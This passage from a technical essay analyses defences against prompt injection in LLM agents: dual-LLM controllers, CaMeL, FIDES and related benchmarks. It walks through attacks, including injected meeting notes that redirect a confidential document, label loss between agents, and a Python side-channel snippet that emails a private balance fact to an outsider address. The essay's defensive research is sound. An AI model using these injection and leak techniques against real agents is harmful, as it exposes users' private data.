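values = {
    "$VAR2": "You wrote: $VAR1",
    "$VAR1": "Our fee for the loan is £40,000.",
}
reply = "Thank you for your comment. $VAR2"
```

for name, text in values.items():
    reply = reply.replace(name, text)
```

The loop inserts the summary, then finds "$VAR1" inside it and replaces that with the email. The museum's public reply now reads "Thank you for your comment. You wrote: Our fee for the loan is £40,000." The email's text appears there even though the privileged model's template included only `$VAR2`.

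Changing the order doesn't solve the problem. If the loop started with `$VAR1`, this reply would be safe, but hostile text in `$VAR1` could pull in a private `$VAR2`. Once there were ten variables, the loop would also turn `$VAR10` into the lender's email followed by a zero, even without an attacker, because `$VAR10` begins with `$VAR1`. A programmer who noticed this might replace the highest numbers first, which is the order that leaked the fee.

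The PHP manual has a warning about this kind of mistake. In one example from its entry on *str_replace*, replacing "a" with "apple" and then "p" with "pear" turns "a p" into "apearpearle pear".

A single pass over the privileged model's template avoids both faults:

```python
import re

template = "Thank you for your comment. $VAR2"

reply = re.sub(
    r"\$VAR\d+",
    lambda match: values[match.group()],
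    template,
)
```

This code searches the template from left to right and never searches the text it has inserted. The public reply therefore contains the characters "$VAR1", which look odd but reveal nothing. The pattern matches every digit after `$VAR`, so the code can't replace the `$VAR1` inside `$VAR10`. If a name doesn't exist, the code raises an error and posts nothing. PHP's `strtr` function also makes only one pass and replaces the longest matching name, according to PHP Tips' *strtr() Does Only One Pass*.

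The fault returns if another part of the program treats the finished reply as a template. *The War on SQLi* (WordPress, 2017) describes a case in WordPress, where a function builds database queries by replacing placeholders such as `%s` with values. Some code ran the function on part of a query and then again on the whole query. If a user's text resembled a placeholder, the second run replaced it, and an attacker could use this to change the query.

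WordPress released a fix in September 2017, but the fix made some previously safe queries vulnerable. The team considered making the second run an error but decided that this would break too many plugins. Six weeks later, it released a version that replaces each percent sign in a value with a long string, so that the value can't be treated as a placeholder. The copy of the code in WP Kama's *wpdb::placeholder_escape* shows that WordPress generates the string from a unique identifier and a secret key, which makes it hard to guess.

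### References that text can't imitate

A controller can also make its names hard to guess. If each name included 128 random bits, someone writing an email in advance would have a one in 2¹²⁸ chance of guessing a particular name. An injection couldn't get the quarantined model to reveal a name either, because the controller replaces the names before that model sees the prompt.

Protect AI's *Deanonymize Scanner*, a tool that puts personal details back into a model's output, uses placeholders such as `[REDACTED_PERSON_1]`. The closing bracket distinguishes person 1 from person 10, but anyone could guess a placeholder and write it in an email.

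It is safer not to search the text for names at all. The privileged model can return its reply in parts, with each reference as a separate type of object:

```python
reply = ["Thank you for your comment. ", Ref(2)]
```

The controller looks up the text for the placeholder `Ref(2)` and treats every string as content. If an email contains the characters "Ref(2)", the controller doesn't look them up, because they are part of a string. Parameterised queries protect a database in the same way.

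Costa and colleagues use typed references in one of their agent designs. Each argument to a tool is either literal text or a variable, and the program looks up each variable once. They can also restrict the model's output so that it names only existing variables.

Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (May 2026) announced a version of this idea as an experimental feature of the company's Agent Framework. By default, the framework stores untrusted tool results and shows the main model only references to them. A second model without tools can process the stored text.

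The framework has to identify which results are untrusted. Microsoft's announcement warns that the framework treats unlabeled tools as trusted, so their output would go straight to the main model. Microsoft's documentation, however, says the framework treats them as untrusted by default. A developer should label every tool and test what the main model receives.

The documentation is also unclear about summaries. It says that the second model's output goes back into storage as untrusted, but also that the main model can reason over the summary. Under Willison's rule, the main model would see only the summary's name.

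The privileged model can still refer to the wrong text. If it mistakenly puts a reference to the lender's email in a public reply, the controller will insert the email as instructed. Preventing that requires a separate rule about who may receive the email.

### What the design costs

Willison calls the design "pretty bad", partly because it is complicated to build. Every new feature could give untrusted text another route to the privileged model, and a single leak undoes the protection. For example, if the user asks a follow-up question about a summary and the assistant builds its next prompt from the conversation on the screen, the privileged model will read the untrusted summary. An error message that quotes the email's subject line could cause the same problem.

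A programmer can look for such leaks by putting a random string in a test email and searching for it in every prompt sent to the privileged model. The test should include follow-up questions and failed tool calls. It would still miss text that the quarantined model had reworded.

The assistant also becomes less useful, because the privileged model can't react to what it isn't allowed to read. Costa and colleagues define the tasks that remain possible. Let *A*(*d*) be the set of action sequences that complete a task when the user's data is *d*. The task is *data independent* if

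⋂ *A*(*d*) ≠ ∅,

where the intersection covers every possible *d*. In other words, at least one fixed sequence of actions works whatever the data contains. Summarising the latest email meets this condition. Completing today's tasks from a to-do list doesn't, because the assistant has to know what the tasks are before it can choose its tools. *Twin Agent* (2026) points out the same limit in agents that plan everything in advance, since the plan can't use information that emerges during the work.

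Willison's opening example is a request to add an email's action items to a to-do list. This works if the to-do tool accepts the whole list as one value. If the tool requires a separate call for each item, the privileged model needs at least the number of items, which the controller could safely pass to it. Microsoft offers a less restrictive solution, a tool that lets the main model read a stored text and records that it did so. But the main model, which has tools, is then reading untrusted text, so safety depends on the framework's limits on those tools.

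Hiding text from the privileged model doesn't protect data that the quarantined model can see. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* describes an assistant whose quarantined model drafts a reply to an email. An attacker's email could get that model to hide private information in the draft, which the privileged model would send without reading. The quarantined model should therefore receive only the private data that the task requires. More generally, the design controls which actions run but not the values that go into them (*CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too*, 2026). CaMeL addresses this weakness.

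The user can also be deceived, because the controller displays whatever the quarantined model wrote. The controller can identify exactly which words came from `$VAR2`, so it can put them in a box labelled "Summary of an outside email" and show them without links or images. This makes the source clear, but the user may still believe a false statement in the box.

Willison generally distrusts AI filters for prompt injection, but suggests that a model might be useful for warning people about messages with instructions to copy and paste strange text. An unnecessary warning would do little harm. The controller has no comparable protection when a user pastes a stranger's text into a request, because the privileged model treats everything in the user's request as trusted.

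### Six patterns

*Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* includes Willison's design among six ways to build safer agents, and calls the controller an "orchestrator". All six follow the principle that once an agent has read untrusted text, that text must not be able to trigger a harmful action, and all six use ordinary software to enforce this.

| Pattern | Restriction on the model | Job of the ordinary software |
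|---|---|---|
| Action selector | It picks from a list of actions and doesn't see the results | Run the chosen action |
| Plan then execute | It commits to its actions before reading outside data | Refuse any action outside the plan |
| Map-reduce | A separate model without tools reads each document | Check the answers and, in some versions, combine them |
| Dual LLM | The model with tools handles only names | Store the text and replace the names |
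| Code then execute | It writes a program before any outside text arrives | Run the program |
| Context minimisation | It writes the answer without seeing the user's original prompt | Remove the prompt |

The first five patterns rely on a relay program to pass the model's choices or text to tools or other models. Context minimisation depends more on deleting text. For example, a shop's chatbot can turn a customer's question into a database query and then discard the question, so an instruction in it can't affect how the model presents the results.

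Map-reduce is a special case of Willison's design. In the paper's example, an agent must find this month's invoices and email them to the accounts department. A separate model reads each file and answers only whether it is an invoice. Text in a hostile file can cause that file to be included but can't affect the decision on any other file. This protection would fail if the model that sends the email also read the selected files, so the program should attach them without showing them to that model.

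The patterns can also be combined with templates. For a recruiter, the privileged model might write a sentence saying how many more years of experience one candidate has than another, with placeholders for the details. Quarantined models extract each candidate's years of experience, and ordinary code subtracts one from the other. A candidate can still lie about the number, but can't rewrite the sentence if the code accepts only numbers for that placeholder.

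*Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* suggests that a coding agent should see outside documentation only as a strictly formatted list of functions, with names of at most 30 characters. In a post about the paper, Willison doubts that this is safe, because a function's name could suggest a harmful command. Thirty letters, digits and underscores can hold up to about 179 bits, enough for a short instruction. The controller could replace the names with numbers, but the agent would then know much less about what each function did.

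## CaMeL: an interpreter that records where each value came from

With Willison's controller, the user's request determines which tools run, but untrusted text can still determine what those tools receive. Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues at Google DeepMind identified this gap in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025). In their example, a user asks an assistant to send Bob the document he requested at their last meeting. The meeting notes contain Bob's email address and the document's name.

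The privileged model can plan every step without reading the notes, but the quarantined model has to read them to find the address. An instruction planted in the notes could make that model return an attacker's address, and the controller would then send the document there. The attacker might not need prompt injection, because anyone who can edit the notes can replace Bob's address. Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, accepts the criticism and says the flaw was new to him.

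The DeepMind team's solution is CaMeL, short for "capabilities for machine learning". It keeps the two models but replaces the controller with an interpreter, a program that runs code step by step. The interpreter records where each value came from and who may read it, and checks those records before each tool call.

### The document request, line by line

The privileged model turns the user's request into a program in a restricted form of Python, a language that models already write well. For Bob's document, a simplified version might be:

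```python
notes = find_notes("last meeting with Bob")
address = ask_quarantined("Find Bob's email address", notes, EmailStr)
title = ask_quarantined("Find the document Bob wants", notes, str)
document = fetch_document(title)
send_email(to=address, subject="Your document", attachment=document)
```

The interpreter attaches a provenance label to every result. If it computes a value *z* from *x* and *y*, the labels combine as follows:

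sources(*z*) = sources(*x*) ∪ sources(*y*)

readers(*z*) = readers(*x*) ∩ readers(*y*)

The new value therefore has all the sources of its inputs, and only people who may read both inputs may read it.

Suppose the user can edit the notes, and so can Bob and a contractor called Carol. Bob is allowed to read the document, a loan agreement, but Carol is not. Before the user makes the request, Carol replaces Bob's address in the notes with her own. The table shows the labels but omits the user's request, which is a source of every value.

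| Value | Content | Other sources | Permitted readers |
|---|---|---|---|
| `notes` | The altered notes | Notes file | User, Bob, Carol |
| `address` | Carol's address | Notes file | User, Bob, Carol |
| `title` | "Loan agreement" | Notes file | User, Bob, Carol |
| `document` | The agreement | Notes file, document store | User, Bob |

The first line only finds the notes, which the policy always allows. On the second line, the interpreter requires the quarantined model's answer to be in the form of an email address. Carol's address passes this check, which a paragraph of instructions would fail. The third line extracts the correct title. On the fourth, the interpreter records the notes file as one of the document's sources because the notes determined which document to fetch.

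Before running the last line, the interpreter calls the policy for sending email. *CaMeLoT* (2026) describes these policies as Python functions that inspect a tool call and its arguments, then allow or deny the call and give a reason. A simple one for this task would be:

```python
def email_policy(to, attachment):
    if to.value in attachment.readers:
        return "allow", "The recipient may read the document."
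    return "deny", "The recipient may not read the document."
```

Carol is not a permitted reader, so the interpreter stops the call. If the notes had contained Bob's address, the interpreter would have sent the email. If Bob changed the title in the notes to "Staff salaries", the same policy would prevent the interpreter from sending him that file unless he was already allowed to read it.

The same policy can block a legitimate request. Bob may be an outside client who asked for the agreement because he can't open it. The policy would reject his real address for the same reason as Carol's, and the program would have to ask the user.

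CaMeL's designers call the labels capabilities, but each label describes a piece of data, whereas Hardy's capabilities authorise their holder to use a file. GitHub's integrity levels also depend on where text came from, but they control what an agent reads. CaMeL's labels instead follow each value to the tool that uses it.

The design can also improve privacy. The privileged model receives only the request, so the company that runs it never gets the notes or the agreement. Extracting an address is easier than writing a program, so the quarantined model could be a small one on the user's own computer.

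### What the guarantee covers

*Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) separates CaMeL's protection into two parts. The first, *control-flow integrity*, means that every tool call follows a plan based only on the user's request and other trusted information. Untrusted data can influence which branch of the program runs, but can't add one. The second is a policy check on the data passed to each tool. Without any policies, CaMeL would still prevent the notes from adding a command to delete the user's files, but it would send the agreement to Carol.

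Control-flow integrity protects less as the plan allows more. In *The LLMbda Calculus*, Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) ran CaMeL without policies on a task that involved reading a file and following the instructions inside. The privileged model wrote a loop with a branch for each tool, so the file's contents determined which tools were called. Two attacks succeeded even though every call was part of the plan, because the plan allowed almost anything.

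The guarantee also assumes that the user's request is trustworthy and the policies are correct, as *SoK* (2026) points out. It further depends on CaMeL's interpreter tracking every flow of information. Garby and colleagues note that nobody has proved that it does, and that CaMeL's designers call such a formal treatment a "crucial direction" for further work.

### Results on AgentDojo

Debenedetti and colleagues tested CaMeL on AgentDojo, a benchmark of 97 tasks in simulated office, travel, banking and Slack environments. Its 629 security tests combine these tasks with injected goals. *Treating the Model as an Untrusted Component* (Aljumaily, Alseelawi and Alshabandar, 2026) reports that CaMeL solved 77% of the tasks, compared with 84% for an undefended system. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (Tallam and Miller, 2025) reports 67%, which appears to come from the first version of the CaMeL paper.

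Two injections were counted as successful in CaMeL's own evaluation, and Garby and colleagues explain why neither broke CaMeL's rules. In one, the user had asked the assistant to make a payment described in a document, and the attacker had changed the document. In the other, the assistant quoted hotel reviews word for word, and AgentDojo's scoring program wrongly scored the quoted text as a successful attack.

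The protection increases token use. In tests with GPT-4o, *Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) found that CaMeL used 2.82 times as many input tokens and 2.73 times as many output tokens as an undefended agent on the median task.

Later tests by other teams found much lower completion rates. *SecureClaw* (2026) ran CaMeL's published code through an adapter and reported that none of the 629 attacks succeeded, but CaMeL completed only 29 of the 97 tasks run without an attack. SecureClaw, the rival system presented in the same paper, completed 59 and let four attacks through. Garby and colleagues found that CaMeL completed 18 of 48 runs of the banking tasks with its policies on, about half as many as with them off. Differences in models, policies and the adapter could all have contributed to the gap between these results and the earlier 77%, so developers would need to test their own tasks before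 expecting that figure.

Garby and colleagues also examined how much of the security came from fixing the plan. In 97 of the 144 banking combinations, the attack needed an action that the user's task would never include, so the fixed plan was normally enough to stop it. The other 47 could have succeeded within a legitimate plan. The team ran each of those three times on a model called MiMo-v2.5 with the policies off, and only three of the 141 attacks succeeded. Turning the policies on stopped those three as well, but also cut the number of completed tasks by about half. The policies might be more valuable than this test suggests against an attacker who writes injections specifically to change one address or account number.

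### False content and side channels

CaMeL can't check whether a value is true. A genuine bill and a forged one in the same file have the same label, so a policy lets the assistant pay both or neither. Carol could also change the notes to name an old version of the loan agreement. Bob is allowed to read that version, so the policy would let the assistant send it.

The assistant's final answer can also mislead the user, as it can with Willison's controller. Tallam and Miller suggest having another model check answers for suspicious instructions.

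Information can leak without any forbidden value reaching a tool. *PolicySniff* (2026) lists three of these *side channels* that CaMeL's designers considered: a web request that happens only if a private value meets some condition, an error that changes what happens next, and the timing of an action. Tallam and Miller add a loop that fetches a web page once for each unit of a private number, so the website's owner can learn the number by counting the requests.

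CaMeL has a strict mode that deals with the conditional requests and errors its designers describe. If a program makes a decision using private data, the interpreter treats the actions that depend on that decision as private too. It also gives programs no access to a clock, which its designers' timing example needs. But Garby and colleagues found a way around the tracking of conditions. A program of this form would work:

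```python
low = True
rich = True

if balance > 10_000:
    low = False
if low:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("outsider@example.com", "Rich")
```

Suppose the balance is £20,000. The program sets `low` to false, and the interpreter marks `low` as private because the change depended on the balance. The program then skips the line that would change `rich`, so the interpreter never marks `rich` as private. The email therefore goes out and reveals that the balance is above £10,000.

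Garby and colleagues also found that the label tracking does not cover the code that retries a failed program. Whether a policy blocked an attempt can reveal one bit of a secret, and repeated attempts could reveal the rest.

These leaks are gaps in the interpreter, but an outsider would struggle to exploit them. The privileged model writes the program without reading untrusted text, so an injection in the notes can't add the lines above. The model would write something similar only if the user's own request led it to.

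### Policies and approvals

A policy for emailing documents has to check the recipient and the document together. Willison illustrates CaMeL with a request to email Bob a reminder about a meeting, and a policy that allows the email if the recipient is trusted. That policy is enough for the reminder, because the privileged model wrote the message. It would fail for the document request if the user had typed Bob's address. The recipient would then be trusted, but the notes would still determine which document is attached, and Bob could edit them to request the staff salaries.

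A large organisation might need hundreds of these functions, one for each tool. Tallam and Miller warn that this leads to duplicated and inconsistent rules, and they recommend writing shared rules in a language designed for access policies. *CaMeLoT* notes that each policy checks only one tool call at a time, which makes it awkward to require an assistant that cancels a hotel booking to make a new one before it finishes.

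Strict policies lead to more requests for approval, so users click through more of them carelessly, which Willison's controller was meant to avoid. Willison points out that even the security researcher Troy Hunt fell for a phishing attack while jet-lagged. A user who has approved Bob's real address ten times might approve Carol's on the eleventh. The approval screen should therefore show where the address came from, which CaMeL's labels make possible.

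Garby and colleagues reduced the need for approvals in their own agent by letting the privileged model's program declare an untrusted value trusted. The agent completed about as many banking tasks as CaMeL did without policies, and resisted all but two of 1,296 attacks. In both failures, the program had declared the contents of a file trusted, and the attacker had replaced the file with a false payment request.

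### Losing the labels between agents

Provenance labels protect a value only as long as they stay attached to it. Peters-Gill and colleagues built a system of three agents, each running CaMeL. One agent read a database of job applicants, another sent notifications, and a third coordinated the two. The user asked the system to send Julie a summary of the applicants on Slack, but the database contained an instruction to email the data to an outsider.

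The coordinating agent correctly treated the summary as untrusted, but then pasted it into a written request to the notification agent, which treated the whole request as coming from its user. The notification agent's privileged model read the planted instruction and added an email to its program. The agents had no policies in this test, but a policy based on provenance could also have failed, because the summary had lost its label.

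The team's solution sends the instruction and the untrusted values separately, much as a parameterised query separates a command from its data. In a multi-agent version of AgentDojo, attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time without CaMeL, 0.2% of the time with separate CaMeL agents, and never with this solution. The weakness was rare in that benchmark, but an attacker who knew how the agents communicated could target it.

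### FIDES: labels with a more flexible plan

CaMeL's privileged model can't read a tool's result and then change its plan. FIDES, a 2025 Microsoft design by Costa and colleagues, lets the planning model work one step at a time. It gives each value an integrity label, trusted or untrusted, and a confidentiality label listing who may read it. The planning model sees trusted results directly, while the program hides untrusted ones behind variable names.

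The planning model can open a hidden value, but everything it does afterwards counts as untrusted. A developer can require either or both of two main policies for a particular tool. One allows an important action only if the decision and its arguments are trusted. The other allows the agent to send data only to people who are allowed to read it.

Costa and colleagues compared FIDES with a basic agent on AgentDojo, using GPT-4o for both. The table shows the percentage of tasks each completed when not under attack.

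| Environment | Basic agent, no checks | Basic agent with checks | FIDES with checks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Office | 75.0% | 37.0% | 59.0% |
| Travel | 70.0% | 73.0% | 41.0% |
| Banking | 98.8% | 37.5% | 52.5% |
| Slack | 93.3% | 20.0% | 47.6% |

Hiding untrusted values allowed some tasks to be completed that the checks would otherwise have blocked, except in the travel environment, where GPT-4o often misused the variables. With OpenAI's o1, a stronger reasoning model, FIDES completed 68% of travel tasks.

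The team counted 152 successful attacks against the basic agent without checks, 21 against FIDES without checks, and none against either agent with checks. The team had labelled as untrusted exactly the fields that AgentDojo's attacks use. The result therefore shows that the checks work when the labels are right, but it doesn't measure how often a developer would label a new system correctly.

The confidentiality guarantee covers data that the agent sends directly. Someone who can see which tools the agent calls might still infer something private, and the guarantee doesn't cover timing.

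*Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) extends FIDES to ask for fewer approvals. If an email contains ten jobs that each need an important action, the agent can ask the user once whether to trust the email instead of asking for ten approvals. The agent also has the policies in advance, so it can take them into account when planning. On AgentDojo, these changes reduced the number of approvals by a factor of up to 1.9 compared with FIDES.

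Kolluri and colleagues counted the approvals the agent would have needed and assumed the user would grant them, so they did not measure whether people consider requests more carefully when there are fewer of them. Trusting a whole email also gives up more control, because the agent may carry out an eleventh job that an attacker has hidden in it.

### Letting only restricted data types cross

Jacob and colleagues make the plan flexible in another way by letting the privileged model read the quarantined model's answers as long as they contain no free text. They tested this on three kinds of agent. The table compares the agents on task success without an attack and on the success of a prepared injection.

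| Agent | Tasks completed, undefended | Tasks completed, defended | Attacks succeeding, undefended | Attacks succeeding, defended |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Shopping | 21.8% | 22.4% | 31.7% | 0% |
| Calendar | 90.0% | 91.0% | 63.0% | 0% |
| Bug fixing | 68.3% | 45.0% | 98.9% | 0% |

The calendar agent lost nothing because meeting times are easy to express as one-hour slots. The quarantined model reads the other person's emails and returns the slots that person suggested. The privileged model compares these with the user's calendar, and the model that writes the reply never sees the emails.

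A bug report is much harder to reduce to a list. In this design, the quarantined model returns the bug's category, the numbers of the relevant files and the lines to examine. Another model uses these to write three repair plans without seeing the report. A judge that has read the report returns only the number of the best plan, and the privileged model makes the repair. The lost detail probably explains why the defended agent fixed far fewer bugs.

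Jacob and colleagues go too far in describing the resulting code changes as guaranteed to be safe. Whoever writes the report can't insert an instruction, but may be able to choose which file the agent edits. A false report could direct the agent to a working password check, with the category "improper permissions", and the agent might damage the check while trying to repair it. A project would still need tests and a human review before accepting the change.

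### Testing policies, approval and taint tracking

Aljumaily and colleagues compared ways of controlling an agent's actions without relying on the agent's model. They wrote thirteen tasks with twelve simulated tools, including tools for sending email and changing the settings of industrial equipment. Only some of their results come from real language models; the rest are from simulations and should be considered separately.

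The measured results come from two small open models from 2024, Qwen2.5-1.5B and Qwen2.5-7B, each attacked 156 times under each defence. The attacks were not adapted to the defence.

| Defence | Attacks succeeding, 1.5B | Attacks succeeding, 7B | Normal tasks completed, 1.5B | Normal tasks completed, 7B |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 66% | 86% | 50% | 99% |
| Warning in the prompt | 65% | 55% | 59% | 100% |
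| Marked text and a model-based detector | 10% | 0% | 37% | 100% |
| List of permitted tools | 42% | 67% | 78% | 99% |
| Strict checks on arguments | 9% | 22% | 68% | 95% |
| Permissions specific to the task | 1% | 8% | 71% | 99% |

The task-specific permissions also included a rule against sending out confidential data. With these permissions, the models still requested the attacker's action in 64% and 84% of attacks, so most of the protection came from the program's checks. All fourteen successful attacks involved the same task, in which the agent had permission to write a report and the attacker made it write a false one. The smaller model completed more normal tasks with these permissions than without them, because the program also blocked the model's mistakes.

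The low success rates partly result from the test's design, as Aljumaily and colleagues acknowledge. They used the same definition of an authorised action to set the permissions and to score the attacks, whereas real permissions would probably contain mistakes. The detector's perfect result on the larger model is also weak evidence of how it would perform against an attacker who studies it and rewrites the injection.

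The team also ran the checking code without a language model on 33 harmful tool calls. Some used tricks such as adding an extra recipient to a list or writing a file path that leads out of a permitted folder. A list of permitted tools let 27 of the calls through, simple argument checks let through 18, strict argument checks 6, and task-specific permissions 1.

The results for human approval and taint tracking come only from simulation. *Taint tracking* here means that the program records that an agent has read untrusted text and then requires approval for more of its actions. The simulated reviewer catches up to 90% of harmful requests at first and fewer as requests accumulate. Under these assumptions, and with a model that always obeys the attacker, adding approval and taint tracking to task-specific permissions reduced the average harm from 0.69 to 0.26 on a ten-point scale.

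In the simulation, every run with approval and taint tracking but no permissions ended in a severe action, because the model kept making requests until the reviewer missed one. Automatically refusing everything after the first request for approval in each task reduced the share to 17.3% of runs.

These numbers depend on how the simulated reviewer behaves, and no real reviewer took part. The team also built the simulation on the assumption that a model would obey attacks more often the higher they ranked on a scale of strength. That assumption failed a test in which Qwen2.5-1.5B obeyed one attack 50% of the time and the next one up the scale only 4%.

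The case for limiting requests needs much weaker assumptions. If a reviewer independently misses each harmful request with probability *m*, the chance of missing at least one in *n* requests is

1 − (1 − *m*)ⁿ.

With *m* = 0.1, an attacker who can make twenty requests has an 88% chance of getting at least one approved. Allowing only two requests reduces the chance to 19%, but a user with three legitimate actions to approve would then have to start a new task.
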